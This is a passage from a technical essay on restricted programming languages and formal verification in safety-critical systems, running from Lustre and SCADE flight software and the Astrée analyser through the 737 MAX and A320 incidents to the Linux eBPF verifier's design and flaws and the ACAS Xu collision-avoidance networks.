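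Temporary speed restrictions on the Cambrian line did not pass through the interlocking, so it was not involved in the incident, and a perfect proof of its equations would have held throughout. On HS1, the high-speed line between London and the Channel Tunnel, the interlocking itself stores the restrictions and keeps them through a restart, according to HS1's account in *RAIB Report* (Stewart, 2024), a letter from the UK rail regulator.

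A language that allowed only single-task programs, like Line 14's, might have helped, although this restriction has nothing to do with loops. One part of such a program cannot stop while the rest keeps sending normal status messages. If the task stops, its messages stop too, and even a simple connection check will detect that.

The remedy on the Cambrian line was simpler. Since May 2022 the radio block centre has kept temporary restrictions in memory that survives a restart. The same product on a French high-speed line had received this change years earlier, for convenience, which removed the hazard without anybody realising it was there. The Cambrian safety case relied on the French documents from before the change. The case for the new software's integrity rests on compliance with the European development standards. Stewart explains that Network Rail's tests were not a significant part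 of that case, because testing cannot guarantee what software will do. Earlier editions of the same standards applied to the original system, which entered service without the product safety case they prescribe.

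## Airliner flight control: synchronous languages and static analysis

On Line 14, engineers had to prove loop by loop that the work in each cycle would finish. Flight-control software also runs in short cycles, but engineers write much of it in SCADE, the industrial form of an academic language called Lustre. They don't need those proofs because a cycle that runs forever can't be written in SCADE. *Synchronous Observers Revisited for Runtime Verification of Lustre Using STL*, a 2026 research paper, describes Lustre as the most widely used of the classic synchronous languages, mainly because of SCADE's use in aviation.

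A Lustre program is a set of equations, and each variable has one value per tick of a clock. This one keeps a running total:

```
node total(i: int; reset: bool) returns (s: int);
let
  s = 0 -> if reset then 0 else pre s + i;
tel
```

The arrow separates the value on the first tick from the rule for every later tick, and `pre s` is the value of s one tick earlier. If i is 5, 3, 4 and 2 on four successive ticks, and reset is true only on the last, then s is 0, 3, 7 and 0. *Teaching Synchronous Dataflow Modelling with Learn-Heptagon* (2026) introduces students to the language with nearly the same program.

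The compiler sorts the equations so that each comes after the ones it depends on, then turns each into a few instructions. The compiled program runs the whole list once per tick. If a programmer wrote `s = s + i`, without `pre`, s would depend on itself within a single tick and the compiler would reject the program. The program's memory is fixed too. *Synthesizing Modular Invariants for Synchronous Code* (2014) explains that a program can look back only a limited number of ticks, and that this limit follows from its text. The running total, for example, has to store one number between ticks. A programmer could not write a program that stored every airspeed reading since take-off. *Synchronous Programming with Refinement Types* (2024) counts this restriction as an advantage because it makes memory use predictable.

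SCADE combines Lustre with features of Esterel, another academic language, according to *Specifying a Cryptographical Protocol in Lustre and SCADE* (2020). Engineers usually draw SCADE programs as block diagrams, a notation control engineers already use, and a compiler turns them into conventional code.

Programmers in these languages assume each tick takes no time. This is harmless as long as the computer finishes each tick before the next inputs arrive. As on Line 14, engineers have to check that deadline separately, for example with aiT, which *Probabilistic Interval Analysis of Unreliable Programs* (2024) describes as an analyser of worst-case execution time.

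### From one tick to a whole flight

At a hundred ticks a second, a ten-hour flight has 3.6 million ticks, and some questions about the whole run are much harder than any question about one tick. Imagine a primitive machine with two counters, a and b, and three numbered instructions. Instruction 1 adds one to b and goes to 2. Instruction 2 goes to 3 if a is zero, and otherwise subtracts one from a and goes back to 1. Instruction 3 stops. A Lustre program can carry out one of these instructions per tick:

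```
node machine(start: int) returns (line, a, b: int);
let
  line = 1 -> if pre line = 1 then 2
              else if pre line = 2 and pre a > 0 then 1
              else 3;
  a = start -> if pre line = 2 and pre a > 0 then pre a - 1
               else pre a;
  b = 0 -> if pre line = 1 then pre b + 1 else pre b;
tel
```

If start is 2, the machine reaches instruction 3 on the seventh tick, with b at 3. Any other two-counter program translates in the same way, with one branch per instruction. Marvin Minsky proved in the 1960s that two counters are enough to simulate any Turing machine if they can hold numbers of any size. An algorithm that could determine, for every Lustre program with unbounded integers, whether `line` ever reaches the stopping instruction would therefore solve the halting problem, so no such algorithm exists. Each tick takes only a few steps, but the program can run for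 an unlimited number of ticks, which gives it the unbounded repetition that the language doesn't allow within a tick.

Real flight computers have integers of limited size, typically 32 bits. As on any finite machine, this makes the question decidable in principle, but that helps little in practice because the three variables above already have 2^96 joint states. Limited integers can also overflow, a failure that a proof about ideal whole numbers would miss. A counter that goes up by one on every tick, a hundred times a second, reaches the largest signed 32-bit number after 248 days. On most processors, the next addition makes it jump to a huge negative value.

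### Running a program on intervals

In *A Static Analyzer for Large Safety-Critical Software* (2003), Blanchet, Mauborgne and colleagues described an analyser, now called Astrée, that looks for this sort of error. It checks C code for overflows, division by zero, out-of-bounds array access and similar faults. Nobody has to write a specification, because these are errors in any program. They designed it for programs that were mostly generated as C code from block diagrams equivalent to Lustre.

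Astrée uses abstract interpretation, which means running a program on descriptions of sets of values instead of on the values themselves. The simplest description is an interval. Suppose a program smooths a sensor reading u, which always lies between −10 and 10:

```
x = 0
on every tick:  x = 0.5 * x + u
```

After one tick x lies in [−10, 10], after two in [−15, 15], and after three in [−17.5, 17.5]. The interval keeps growing towards [−20, 20] but never reaches it, so an analyser that followed it tick by tick would never finish. Instead, the analyser deliberately overestimates, a step called widening. It jumps to an interval such as [−100, 100] and checks whether one more tick could take x outside. Half of 100, plus 10, is 60, so x stays inside, and since it also starts inside, the interval holds for every tick of every flight. The analyser can then tighten its estimate by applying the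 same sum to [−100, 100], which shows that x is always in [−60, 60]. Further rounds give [−40, 40] and [−30, 30]. Each of these intervals is correct, so the analyser can stop after any round.

If a later line divides by x + 50, the analyser has proved that the divisor is never zero. But if it stops at [−30, 30] and a line divides by x + 25, it raises an alarm, which is false because x never leaves [−20, 20]. Intervals also don't record how variables are related. If y is a copy of x, then x − y + 1 is always 1, but the two intervals alone show only that it lies between −59 and 61. Blanchet and colleagues therefore added richer descriptions, such as "octagons", which track the sums and differences of pairs of variables. They also accounted for rounding errors throughout.

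Astrée is sound but not complete, as *Field-Sensitive Value Analysis of Embedded C Programs with Union Types* notes. Its developers nevertheless aimed to eliminate false alarms on one family of programs, because they estimated that at a false-alarm rate of 5%, clearing the alarms on a few hundred thousand lines by hand would take several person-years. They started with a program that had run for ten years without a run-time error, presumed that every alarm was false, traced each one to its cause, and refined the analyser until few or none remained.

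Static analysis has worked well on large flight-control programs. Blanchet and colleagues worked with programs of up to 132,000 lines. *The parallel implementation of the Astrée static analyzer* reports results on two fly-by-wire programs, in which computers carry the pilot's commands to the control surfaces. Astrée analysed the first, which had 70,000 lines, in an hour. The second was much more complex, with 380,000 lines, and took ten and a half hours. Neither analysis produced any false alarms. *Static Analysis of Run-Time Errors in Embedded Real-Time Parallel C Programs* (2012) reports zero false alarms on Airbus control software of up to a million lines, after a few hours on a standard server.

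These figures are weak evidence of how Astrée would perform on unrelated code, because its developers tuned it until it stopped raising alarms on Airbus's programs. But Astrée is sound, so the absence of alarms on those programs amounts to a proof that the errors it looks for cannot occur in them.

The proof assumes a range for each hardware input and a maximum running time, both supplied by the user. Blanchet and colleagues needed the time limit because some counters in these programs go up with every event. With a limit of, say, 100 hours, Astrée can show that the counter in the earlier example never overflows, but the guarantee holds only if somebody restarts the computer in time. Astrée also doesn't check whether the program does what it is meant to do. If an engineer reverses the sign in a control law, so that pulling the stick back pushes the nose down, the program can still be free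 of run-time errors.

### C and Ada with parts removed

C is Turing-complete, but Astrée accepts only a much narrower subset of it. According to *Symbolic Methods to Enhance the Precision of Numerical Abstract Domains*, this subset excludes recursion (functions that call themselves), dynamic memory allocation and concurrent execution. In the programs that Blanchet and colleagues studied, pointers served only to pass variables to functions. Each omission makes the analysis easier. Without recursion, the analyser can treat every function call as if the function's body stood in its place. Without dynamic allocation, it can list every variable in advance. B0, the language of Line 14, left out much the same features.

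Such rules are common well beyond Airbus. MISRA C, a set of guidelines that began in the car industry, prohibits recursion and dynamic allocation. Gerard Holzmann of NASA's Jet Propulsion Laboratory proposed ten rules in 2006, one of which requires every loop to have a fixed upper bound that a tool can easily verify. Loops meant to run forever, such as a controller's main loop, are exempt, but a tool should be able to prove that they never end. Ada programmers can declare certain restrictions in the source code, such as a ban on allocation, and the compiler rejects code that breaks them. SPARK, a subset of Ada designed for formal verification, originally left out pointers and recursion, though later versions allow both under conditions.

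The loop rule changes how people write ordinary calculations. A programmer might naturally refine an estimate until its error is small enough, which could take forever on an unlucky input. Under the rule, the code looks more like this:

```
for (k = 0; k < 8 && error > tolerance; k++) refine();
if (error > tolerance) use_last_good_value();
```

The program can no longer hang here, but someone has to decide whether the last good value is safe to use and for how long.

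C code that follows all these rules does a bounded amount of work in a fixed amount of memory on each tick, just as a Lustre program does. A team can therefore get much of the benefit of a restricted language by combining a general-purpose one with a checker. But an ordinary C compiler accepts code that breaks the rules, so the guarantee depends on people running the checker and refusing exceptions. MISRA C formally allows projects to break most of its rules if they document why.

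### What certification requires

US and European regulators accept the DO-178C standard as a way to show that airborne software is fit to fly. It grades software from level A, where a failure could be catastrophic, to level E, where it has no effect on safety. For each level it sets objectives for the development process and the evidence. Developers must write requirements, trace every piece of code to them and back, test each requirement, and measure how thoroughly the tests exercise the code. The tracing is awkward for a neural network, because its individual weights correspond to no requirement.

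At level A, the tests must show that each condition in a decision can change the outcome by itself. For "a and (b or c)", four of the eight possible tests are enough. The first test sets a and b to true and c to false, which gives true. Making a false turns the result false, which shows that a matters. With a true again, making b false also turns the result false, and then making c true turns it back to true, which shows that b and c matter too. These tests are demanding for the code that exists, but they cannot reveal a condition missing from the requirements.

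DO-178C lets each project choose its programming language, but requires it to write coding standards for that language and check the code against them. DO-333, RTCA's *Formal Methods Supplement to DO-178C and DO-278A* (2011), is optional and also leaves the choice of language open. It sets out how the objectives change when a team uses formal methods, so that a proof can replace some reviews and tests. The team must then use a notation with a precise mathematical meaning, justify that its analysis is sound, and state and justify every assumption behind it.

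According to Military Embedded Systems, DO-333 covers three kinds of method: deductive proof, model checking and abstract interpretation. Cofer and Miller tried all three for NASA on a two-channel flight guidance system. They intended the work to illustrate usable evidence and didn't attempt a complete certification.

If a tool replaces work that people would otherwise check, the developers also have to qualify the tool. According to *Teaching Synchronous Dataflow Modelling with Learn-Heptagon*, the SCADE compiler has been qualified. Qualification rests on evidence about how the tool's makers built and tested it, which is weaker than a proof that its output is always right. Researchers have also developed Lustre compilers with formal proofs of correctness, as *Secure Information Flow Typing in LUSTRE* (2022) mentions. These proofs make the trusted computing base smaller, but neither they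 nor qualification would catch a wrong requirement.

### The 737 MAX: one sensor and a reset rule

Boeing gave the 737 MAX larger engines than its predecessor had and mounted them higher and further forward, which made the control column feel too light near a stall. To correct this, Boeing added a software function called MCAS. When the angle of attack (the angle at which the wing meets the air) became too high in manual flight, MCAS moved the horizontal stabiliser on the tail to push the nose down.

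In October 2018 Lion Air Flight 610 crashed near Jakarta, killing 189 people. In March 2019 Ethiopian Airlines Flight 302 crashed near Addis Ababa, killing 157. The US regulator's review, FAA (2020), found that erroneous data from a single angle-of-attack sensor triggered MCAS. Each time the pilots used the electric trim switch to bring the nose back up and then let go, MCAS reset, and five seconds later it moved the stabiliser again by a fixed amount, whatever the stabiliser's position. After several rounds the pilots could no longer hold the nose up with the elevator, the movable surface on the tail that they controlled directly.

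Simplified and without the five-second delay, the reset rule takes two lines of Lustre. Here `high` is true when the measured angle is too high, and `release` is true when a pilot lets go of the switch:

```
fired   = false -> (pre fired or pre command) and high and not release;
command = high and not fired;
```

Boeing's revised rule allows one command for each high-angle event, and another only after the angle has come down. In the simplified version, this amounts to deleting "and not release". Both the original and revised programs finish every tick, use two bits of memory and contain no run-time errors. A model checker could show within moments that the original repeats its command while the angle stays high and the revised one does not, but only if somebody had thought to specify that property. Even the revised program would issue its one command in response to a false reading.

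The safety consultant Daniels (2020) writes in *Correctness by Construction*, a message on a mailing list for safety engineers, that there is no evidence the MCAS software departed from its requirements. Daniels points instead to a design change that left MCAS dependent on a single sensor and raised how far it could move the stabiliser each time from 0.6 to 2.5 degrees.

The 737's computers have a defence against programming mistakes. According to the avionics blog Satcom Guru (2018), each of the two autopilot computers contains two different processors, programmed by different people. But both groups worked from the same requirements, so if the requirements are wrong, both programs will be wrong even if they implement them faithfully.

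The design wrongly assumed that one sensor's reading would be true and that pilots would recognise and counter a false activation quickly enough. The FAA's review addressed both assumptions. The new software compares two sensors, ignores them if they differ by more than 5.5 degrees, and limits how far MCAS can move the stabiliser. Safe flight may no longer depend on how quickly the crew carries out an emergency procedure. AVweb's *Review Panel* reported that an international panel also found that nobody had evaluated MCAS as a complete, integrated function during certification. Astrée's model of the outside world consists largely of ranges for the inputs, and a sensor that reads 20 degrees too high may still be within its range.

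### The A320: a number that changed in memory

On 30 October 2025, an Airbus A320 on JetBlue Flight 1230 from Cancún to Newark pitched nose-down while cruising in smooth air with the autopilot on. It lost only about 100 feet, but the jolt caused minor injuries to four flight attendants and 18 passengers. These details come from the US National Transportation Safety Board's account, as reproduced by the independent site NTSB Reports (2025).

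Attention soon turned to the elevator and aileron computers (ELACs), which move the surfaces that pitch and roll the aircraft. On 28 November, Airbus (2025) announced that intense solar radiation might corrupt data critical to the flight controls. The same day, European and US regulators issued emergency directives ordering airlines to replace ELAC version L104 in affected aircraft configurations before the next flight. Aviation Week's *EASA Orders Immediate Airbus A320 Flight Control Software Changes* (2025) reported that some 6,000 aircraft were involved. Fewer probably needed work, at least in the United States, where the FAA's *Airworthiness Directives; Airbus SAS Airplanes* (2026) covered 2,007 aircraft but estimated that about 550 might need the change.

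The injuries were minor, but the European regulator's current order, EASA's *Airworthiness Directive 2026-0134* (2026), warns that in the worst case an uncommanded elevator movement could exceed the aircraft's structural limits.

Nearly every proof about source code assumes that memory returns what the program stored in it. If Airbus is right about corrupted data, that assumption failed. In Lustre, `pre s` is defined as the value `s` had on the previous tick. But a high-energy particle that strikes a memory chip can flip a bit and turn a stored 40 into 56, even when every instruction is correct and the computer executes it correctly.

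Engineers have known about this for decades and have ways to deal with it. In *Technical information on Airbus A320 recall?* (Daniels, 2025), the consultant describes working on the Airbus A380's landing-gear system, whose software kept three copies of critical data, one with every bit inverted. With eight-bit numbers, 40 would be stored as 40, 40 and 215. If one 40 changes to 56, inverting the 215 still gives 40, which matches the other copy, so the program can restore the correct value. The coded processor on Line 14 protected against the same kind of fault in a different way.

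The previous version, L103+, evidently coped better, since the remedy was to go back to it. According to AeroMorning, Airbus had developed L104 to reduce the risk of losing control in flight. Daniels guesses that its developers added a function and failed to protect the new data it needed. This guess fits the known facts. A language could prevent this kind of mistake, whether or not its programs always terminate, if its compiler automatically stored every `pre` value in triplicate.

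The cause is still unsettled. In its July 2026 directive, EASA calls the ELAC malfunction a "possible contributing factor", and the NTSB had not issued its final report when New York magazine's *The Mysterious Case of the JetBlue Flight That Went Into Free Fall* (2026) appeared in August. Visual Approach, an aviation newsletter, checked the solar data and found no intense radiation on the day of the flight. A severe radiation storm two weeks later caused no reported incidents. This is good evidence against a solar cause but weak evidence against a bit flip, because cosmic rays from outside the solar system reach aircraft all the time. The Belgian solar-data centre SIDC still considers a single high-energy particle the most likely trigger.

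### How much credit the languages deserve

Daniels (2020) wrote that software failing to meet its requirements had never caused the loss of a passenger aircraft, but that several fatal accidents had happened because software correctly implemented bad requirements. Besides the 737 MAX crashes, Daniels lists an A320 that overran the runway in Warsaw in 1993. This is one expert's summary, not a systematic count, but the accidents discussed here are consistent with it.

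Restricted languages can't be given most of the credit for this record. It covers aircraft programmed in ordinary C, Ada and assembly as well as aircraft programmed in SCADE. All of them were also certified and heavily tested, and their critical systems have backups. No comparable fleet has flown without those protections, so we can't tell how much the language contributes by itself.

On the JetBlue flight, the second ELAC detected a problem within seconds and took over, according to New York magazine. The French investigators' preliminary notice, BEA's *Incident to the Airbus A320 registered N605JB operated by JetBlue*, complicates this account slightly because it places the pitch-down "likely" during a switch between ELACs. Either way, the aircraft recovered because it had more than one computer, and a proof about either computer's source code would not have provided that redundancy.

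The best evidence about the Astrée analyser comes from the program its developers started with, which had already run for ten years without a run-time error before they analysed it. The program's synchronous design and testing may have contributed to that record, but Astrée could not have. Astrée added proof that the record was not luck, and it can check each new version in hours of computing time. This is very useful to a manufacturer that changes its software regularly, provided that the new version's requirements are right and its data stays intact.

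## eBPF: a restricted language inside the Linux kernel

Small teams of specialists wrote the control software for Line 14 and Airbus, and their employers could insist on strict rules. eBPF is a restricted language with a much larger and less disciplined group of users. The Linux kernel enforces eBPF's restrictions automatically whenever somebody loads a program.

Companies that run many servers often want to change what the kernel does, for instance to discard an attack's packets as soon as they arrive. Gbadamosi, Leonardi and colleagues (2024) explain in *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* that rolling out a modified kernel can take weeks or months, because every machine has to stop its work and restart. A kernel module, which is code loaded into a running kernel, avoids the restart but has the kernel's full powers, so a bug in it can crash the machine.

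Linux has offered eBPF as an alternative since December 2014. A programmer writes a small program, usually in C, and a compiler translates it into instructions for a simple virtual machine with 11 registers, each of which holds one number. A part of the kernel called the verifier checks these instructions. If it accepts them, the kernel translates them into the processor's own instructions and runs them whenever a chosen event occurs, such as a packet arriving. The program can call only certain kernel functions, and it can keep data between runs in tables called maps.

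### How the verifier decides

The verifier uses a form of abstract interpretation, as Astrée does. It goes through the program one instruction at a time and records the range of values that each register could hold. Suppose a program counts packets by type in a table with 16 entries, numbered 0 to 15:

```
i = one byte of the packet      i is between 0 and 255
if i > 15, exit                 past this line, i is between 0 and 15
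count[i] = count[i] + 1         safe, because count has entries 0 to 15
```

At the second line the verifier follows both branches. On one, i is between 16 and 255 and the program exits. On the other, i is at most 15, so the access to the table is safe. If the programmer had written `i > 16` by mistake, the range on the third line would include 16, and the verifier would reject the program.

The verifier also rejects programs that use an arbitrary number as a memory address, read memory they have not written, or exit without releasing a lock. A program may hold only one lock at a time, which prevents two programs from each waiting for a lock that the other holds.

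Twenty branches in a row can produce more than a million paths, so the verifier has to take shortcuts. The Linux kernel documentation's *eBPF verifier* describes the main one, called pruning. If the verifier has already accepted the code after some instruction with a variable i between 0 and 15, and it reaches that instruction again with i between 0 and 7, it can skip the rest of that path.

The verifier is meant to be sound, but it is far from complete. Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte (2026), in *Keel*, describe a safe program that it rejects. The program writes n bytes at the start of an 800-byte buffer, with n between 0 and 800, and then writes at most 800 − n bytes after them, so the second write can never go past byte 800. But the verifier stores the second write's starting point and length as separate ranges, both 0 to 800, and adds them to get a possible end at byte 1,600. Astrée's developers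 handled this kind of problem by tracking how variables are related. In the kernel, that would slow verification and add a lot of code that everybody has to trust.

False alarms waste programmers' time, and the error messages don't help much. One study in the programme of an academic workshop (eBPF'26, *Schedule*, 2026) reproduced 235 rejections and found that 47% of them returned only a generic error code. The verdict can also change with the kernel version, and Alden (2025), in *In search of a stable BPF verifier*, writes that new kernels sometimes break existing programs.

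### From no loops to eight million passes

Until 2019 the verifier rejected every program that contained a loop. This was an easy way to guarantee termination, but Corbet (2018) noted in *Bounded loops in BPF programs* that it excluded many useful programs. Programmers worked around the ban by having the compiler unroll loops, copying the body once for each pass. A program could have at most 4,096 instructions, which limited how much they could unroll. Fastabend (2018), a developer working on loop support, described people writing unnatural code and trying one version after another until the verifier accepted it.

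Linux 5.2 raised the limit to a million instructions, and Linux 5.3 allowed bounded loops. The verifier follows such a loop pass by pass, as if the programmer had unrolled it. It stops once it has processed a million instructions, so the verifier itself always halts, as a reader points out in *Comments on "Bounded loops in BPF for the 5.3 kernel"*. eBPF Docs' *Loops in BPF* estimates that a loop of 100 passes over 20 instructions and a few branches uses a few thousand of the million. A loop over every byte of a packet might need 65,535 passes, which can easily exceed the limit.

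Even this modest extension made the verifier much more complicated. The patches in Starovoitov (2019), *bpf: bounded loops and other features*, changed 767 lines of it. To follow a loop counter, the verifier had to track exact constants in more places. Fewer states resembled earlier ones, so pruning worked less well. The first patch alone raised the number of states processed for one existing program from 39,389 to 359,445. The last patch, which Starovoitov called the trickiest of the nine, fixed this by working backwards to find which constants mattered. He reported that existing programs ended up verifying much faster than before. A reviewer said the verifier was now so complex that "it's very easy to miss issues".

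Later versions of Linux moved part of the termination guarantee into kernel functions that count a loop's passes, so the verifier doesn't have to follow every one. Linux 5.13 introduced a function that runs a piece of the program, called a callback, once for each entry in a map. Linux 5.17 added another that runs a callback up to 2^23 (about eight million) times. But two loops of this second kind, one inside the other, can make 2^46 passes, which would take nearly 20 hours at a billion passes a second.

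Linux 6.4 added iterators, which supply a loop with one item at a time. With Nakryiko's patch, *bpf: add support for open-coded iterator loops*, the verifier checks both the case where there is another item and the case where none are left each time the program fetches the next one. It stops checking the loop once another pass would start from a state it has already covered, much as Astrée stops at an interval that no further tick can leave. The loop is then safe however many times it runs, but whether it ends depends on the kernel developers' promise that every iterator eventually runs out.

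*bpf: Introduce may_goto instruction* describes a still newer instruction, which exits a loop once it has run for as long as the kernel allows. The first version used a hidden counter. Machine code in Lothoré (2026), *Adding KASAN support to eBPF*, shows a later version that reads the clock and ends the loop after a quarter of a second. For a control layer, this is more useful than a proof of termination because it sets an actual deadline.

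The verifier's main source file had about 2,000 lines in 2014 and more than 20,000 a decade later. The verifier as a whole has grown by more than this, because verification has also used a second file since Linux 5.5, according to *bpf verifier complexity* (2019).

Programmers can now express a great deal in eBPF, including load balancers, security policies and performance monitoring. *blitmus* (Mohan, 2026) lists locks, atomic operations, large areas of shared memory and, since Linux 6.12, whole schedulers, which decide what each processor works on next. Every run of a program still has to end, but maps keep their data from one run to the next. The two-counter machine from the discussion of Lustre, which carried out one instruction per tick, could carry out one per packet in eBPF.

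Users still want the language to allow more. In *SCEV-based Loop Analysis for the BPF Verifier*, Zingerman (2026) notes that nested loops with modest limits can still exceed a million instructions, and proposes a way to verify ordinary loops without unrolling them. In *BPF: 16-byte values, exceptions, and Rust*, Song (2026) describes work on error handling for Rust programs.

Each of these requests was reasonable, but together they turned a language with no loops into one for writing schedulers. Designers of a restricted language for a control layer should expect similar requests. The shop's refund rules might need no loops at first, but somebody will soon want to add up a customer's refunds over the past year.

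### Flaws in the verifier

All of eBPF's guarantees depend on the verifier being right, and it has often been wrong. *eBPF Security in the Wild* (Chen, Ming and colleagues, 2026) collects 2,766 eBPF flaws from 2016 to 2025. One of its breakdowns assigns 520 of these (19%) to the verifier. Another, whose figures add up to only 2,234, assigns it 389 (17%). Most entries are fixes that developers made to the kernel, and only 197 came from the public database of vulnerabilities, so the total includes many bugs that nobody has shown to be exploitable.

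About two thirds of the flaws were in the runtime, which includes the kernel functions and data structures that eBPF programs use. Analysing a program doesn't help if the function it calls is broken. Only 55 flaws involved excessive iteration, the problem that the ban on loops was supposed to prevent. Locking errors, which can also freeze a machine, accounted for 156.

Chen and colleagues examined 114 of the verifier's flaws more closely. Thirty were mistakes about ranges, and 29 were mistakes about pointers or types. *Evolution of Value Tracking in the BPF Verifier* (Yu, 2026) describes a subtle early range error. In Linux 4.9, the verifier kept one range for each register, with a signed minimum and an unsigned maximum. A computer stores −8 as the same bits as a very large positive number. The verifier could confuse the two and conclude that a register holding −8 was between 0 and 1. Since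 Linux 4.14, it has kept separate signed and unsigned ranges.

Some of the flaws came from eBPF's growth. Linux 5.8 introduced a new type of pointer that might be empty. The verifier used a list of types to forbid arithmetic on such pointers, but nobody added the new type to the list, so the verifier let unsafe programs through. Developers were still fixing several unrelated flaws of this kind in September 2026, according to Kernel Dispatch's *Linux mainline* (2026).

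A restriction is therefore only as reliable as its checker. Atelier B's false rules were a similar weakness on Line 14, but the programmers there were not trying to exploit them. An attacker who can load eBPF programs can look for ones that the verifier wrongly accepts. This also matters for AI agents if a learned model may write code that a checker must approve.

Like Astrée, the verifier has no specification of what a program is supposed to do, so even a perfect verifier would miss many bugs. *Heimdall* (2026) reports nine bugs in real eBPF programs that the verifier had accepted. Developers have acknowledged and fixed eight of them.

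### Fewer users and smaller checkers

The simplest response was to let fewer people load programs. Linux began allowing ordinary users to load some kinds of eBPF program in 2016, but the kernel's default configuration has blocked this since version 5.16. On most systems, the verifier therefore mainly protects administrators from their own mistakes, which is much easier than stopping an attacker.

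Besides bugs in the verifier, leaks caused by the processor were a reason to restrict what unprivileged users could do with eBPF. Modern processors guess which way a branch will go and execute instructions before they know whether the guess is right, which can leak secrets even when the program itself is correct. In May 2025 LWN's *Leading items* (2025) covered a proposal to insert barriers against such leaks, which could let unprivileged users do more with eBPF again.

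Researchers have also proved parts of the verifier correct, using tools such as Agni (discussed in another edition of LWN's *Leading items*, 2025). Agni translates the verifier's C code for each range operation into logical formulas. An SMT solver then looks for input values that lie within their ranges but give a result outside the range the verifier calculated. In 2023 Agni's developers reported checking 16 kernel versions, finding new bugs in older ones, and proving the range analysis sound in the latest. This is a strong result, but it covers only one part of the verifier, and only about a quarter of the verifier flaws in Chen and colleagues' sample concerned ranges. Gbadamosi and colleagues wrote in 2024 that nobody had comprehensively verified the whole verifier, partly because it changes so much with every release.

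Other projects would replace the verifier or give it less to do. *eBPF Research* (Chaignon, 2026) lists an alternative verifier called PREVAIL, designs that rely on the Rust language, and proof-carrying code, in which a program comes with a proof of its own safety. Checking a proof is easy even though finding one can be hard, so the kernel needs only a fairly simple checker and doesn't have to trust whoever found the proof. A proposal to the kernel's developers, *bpf: Introduce proof-based verifier enhancement*, would use such proofs only where the existing verifier gets stuck. For the program with the 800-byte buffer, an SMT solver outside the kernel produces a 33-step proof. The key step is that n + (800 − n) is always 800.

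That proposal's proof checker has about 5,000 lines of C. When Cai and colleagues tried to formalise it, they found 13 bugs, including false rules and steps that it accepted without checking. An attacker could have used some of them to get unsafe programs accepted. The researchers then wrote a replacement, Keel, and proved that it accepts a proof only if the proof's conclusion holds, never misuses memory, and finishes in time proportional to the size of its input. In their tests it was 1.3 times as fast as the original. Keel still depends on the existing verifier to state correctly what needs proving, on the C compiler, and on the researchers' description of how the kernel behaves. But it is much easier to prove a small checker correct than a verifier with 20,000 lines.

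### Compared with what?

Defenders of eBPF can reply that the realistic alternative for most of its users is a kernel module, which gets no automatic checking. In July 2024, a faulty update to CrowdStrike's security software made its Windows kernel driver read beyond the end of a list, crashing about 8.5 million computers by Microsoft's estimate. eBPF's verifier is designed to catch out-of-bounds reads like this one. Even a verifier with hundreds of known flaws catches most such mistakes, while an attacker who can load a kernel module can run any code in the kernel without exploiting a flaw.

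This is a good argument for eBPF when code has to run inside the kernel, as it often does for speed. It is weaker for a typical control layer. The shop's refund monitor can run as an ordinary process, which the operating system already isolates from the rest of the system. If it crashes, refunds stop but the machine keeps working. Most of what eBPF's verifier checks would matter little to the shop, which needs to know whether the monitor follows the refund rules.

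## ACAS Xu: a neural network simple enough to verify

Unlike the hand-written programs discussed so far, a neural network gets its behaviour from training, but it can still be a tightly restricted program with no loops. The most studied examples come from work on ACAS Xu, a drone collision-avoidance system flight-tested on a NASA aircraft in 2014.

When another aircraft comes near, ACAS Xu issues an advisory every second. The advisory is "clear of conflict" (the drone need not turn) or a weak or strong turn to the left or right. It depends on seven values: the distance to the other aircraft, its direction, its heading, the speeds of both aircraft, the time until they lose vertical separation, and the previous advisory.

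The designers calculated a score for every advisory in millions of situations and stored the scores in a table. *Deep Neural Network Compression for Aircraft Collision Avoidance Systems* (Julian, Kochenderfer and Owen, 2018) reports that the full table needed hundreds of gigabytes. Removing entries reduced it to 600 million numbers, which took up over 2 GB. That was still too much for certified aircraft computers, and certifying new hardware is slow and expensive.

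They therefore trained a neural network to approximate the scores. It needed 2.4 MB, about a thousandth of the table's size, but took 50 times as long as the table to produce an advisory. To speed it up, they replaced it with 45 small networks, one for each combination of nine values of the time until loss of separation and five previous advisories. In 10 million simulated encounters, the risk of a near mid-air collision was 1.45 in 10,000 with the final networks and 1.47 in 10,000 with the table.

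Julian and colleagues also tried decision trees, which are chains of yes-or-no comparisons and much easier to read. The trees were larger than the single network, but even at up to 100 MB they chose a different advisory from the table in more than 6% of situations, compared with 2% for the network.

### A program without loops

The 45 networks that most researchers have studied are an early prototype, each with six layers of 50 units. Each unit multiplies the previous layer's outputs by fixed weights, adds the products and a constant, and replaces a negative result with zero. Engineers call this a rectified linear unit, or ReLU. In Lustre, one of these networks would be 305 equations, one for each of the 300 units and five scores, and none would need `pre`.

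A fixed network of this kind is therefore not Turing-complete. It always finishes, after the same amount of computation on every input. Many questions about its behaviour are decidable, including any that compares weighted sums of its inputs and outputs with fixed numbers.

This restriction doesn't make the network understandable or safe. The network has about 13,000 weights, and no particular weight represents a rule such as "turn right if the other aircraft is on the left". A network with random weights obeys the same restriction, but it would be unsafe for steering a drone.

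### Two units by hand

A much smaller network shows how a proof works. It has one input x, two ReLUs and one output y:

```
a = max(0, x)
b = max(0, -x)
y = a + b
```

Suppose x lies between −1 and 2, and we want to prove that y never exceeds 2.5. Interval analysis, the simplest method in Astrée, shows that a is at most 2 and b at most 1, so y is at most 3. This bound is correct but too loose to prove the claim, because the method doesn't take into account that a and b can't both be positive.

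A ReLU is "on" if it passes its input through and "off" if it outputs zero. With two ReLUs there are four cases, and within each case the network is just a linear formula:

- If a is on and b is off, x is between 0 and 2 and y equals x, so y is at most 2.
- If a is off and b is on, x is between −1 and 0 and y equals −x, so y is at most 1.
- If both are on, x must be both at least 0 and at most 0, so x and y are 0.
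- If both are off, x and y are again 0.

The largest possible output is therefore 2, which proves the property.

This example comes from *Reluplex* (Katz, Barrett and colleagues, 2017), the paper that made ACAS Xu a standard test for verification. *Reluplex* states that the network's output always equals its input, but the paper's equations give the absolute value of the input, so −1 produces 1. The mistake doesn't affect the paper's calculation, which uses only inputs between 0 and 1. But if experts can misread a network with two units, we can't expect to understand one with 300 by reading its weights.

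### What Reluplex proved

With 300 ReLUs there are 2^300 cases, or about 10^90, so no computer can check them all. Reluplex avoids most of them by extending the simplex method, a standard way of solving systems of linear constraints. It treats the input and output of each ReLU as separate variables, temporarily allows values that don't satisfy the ReLU function, and corrects them one by one.

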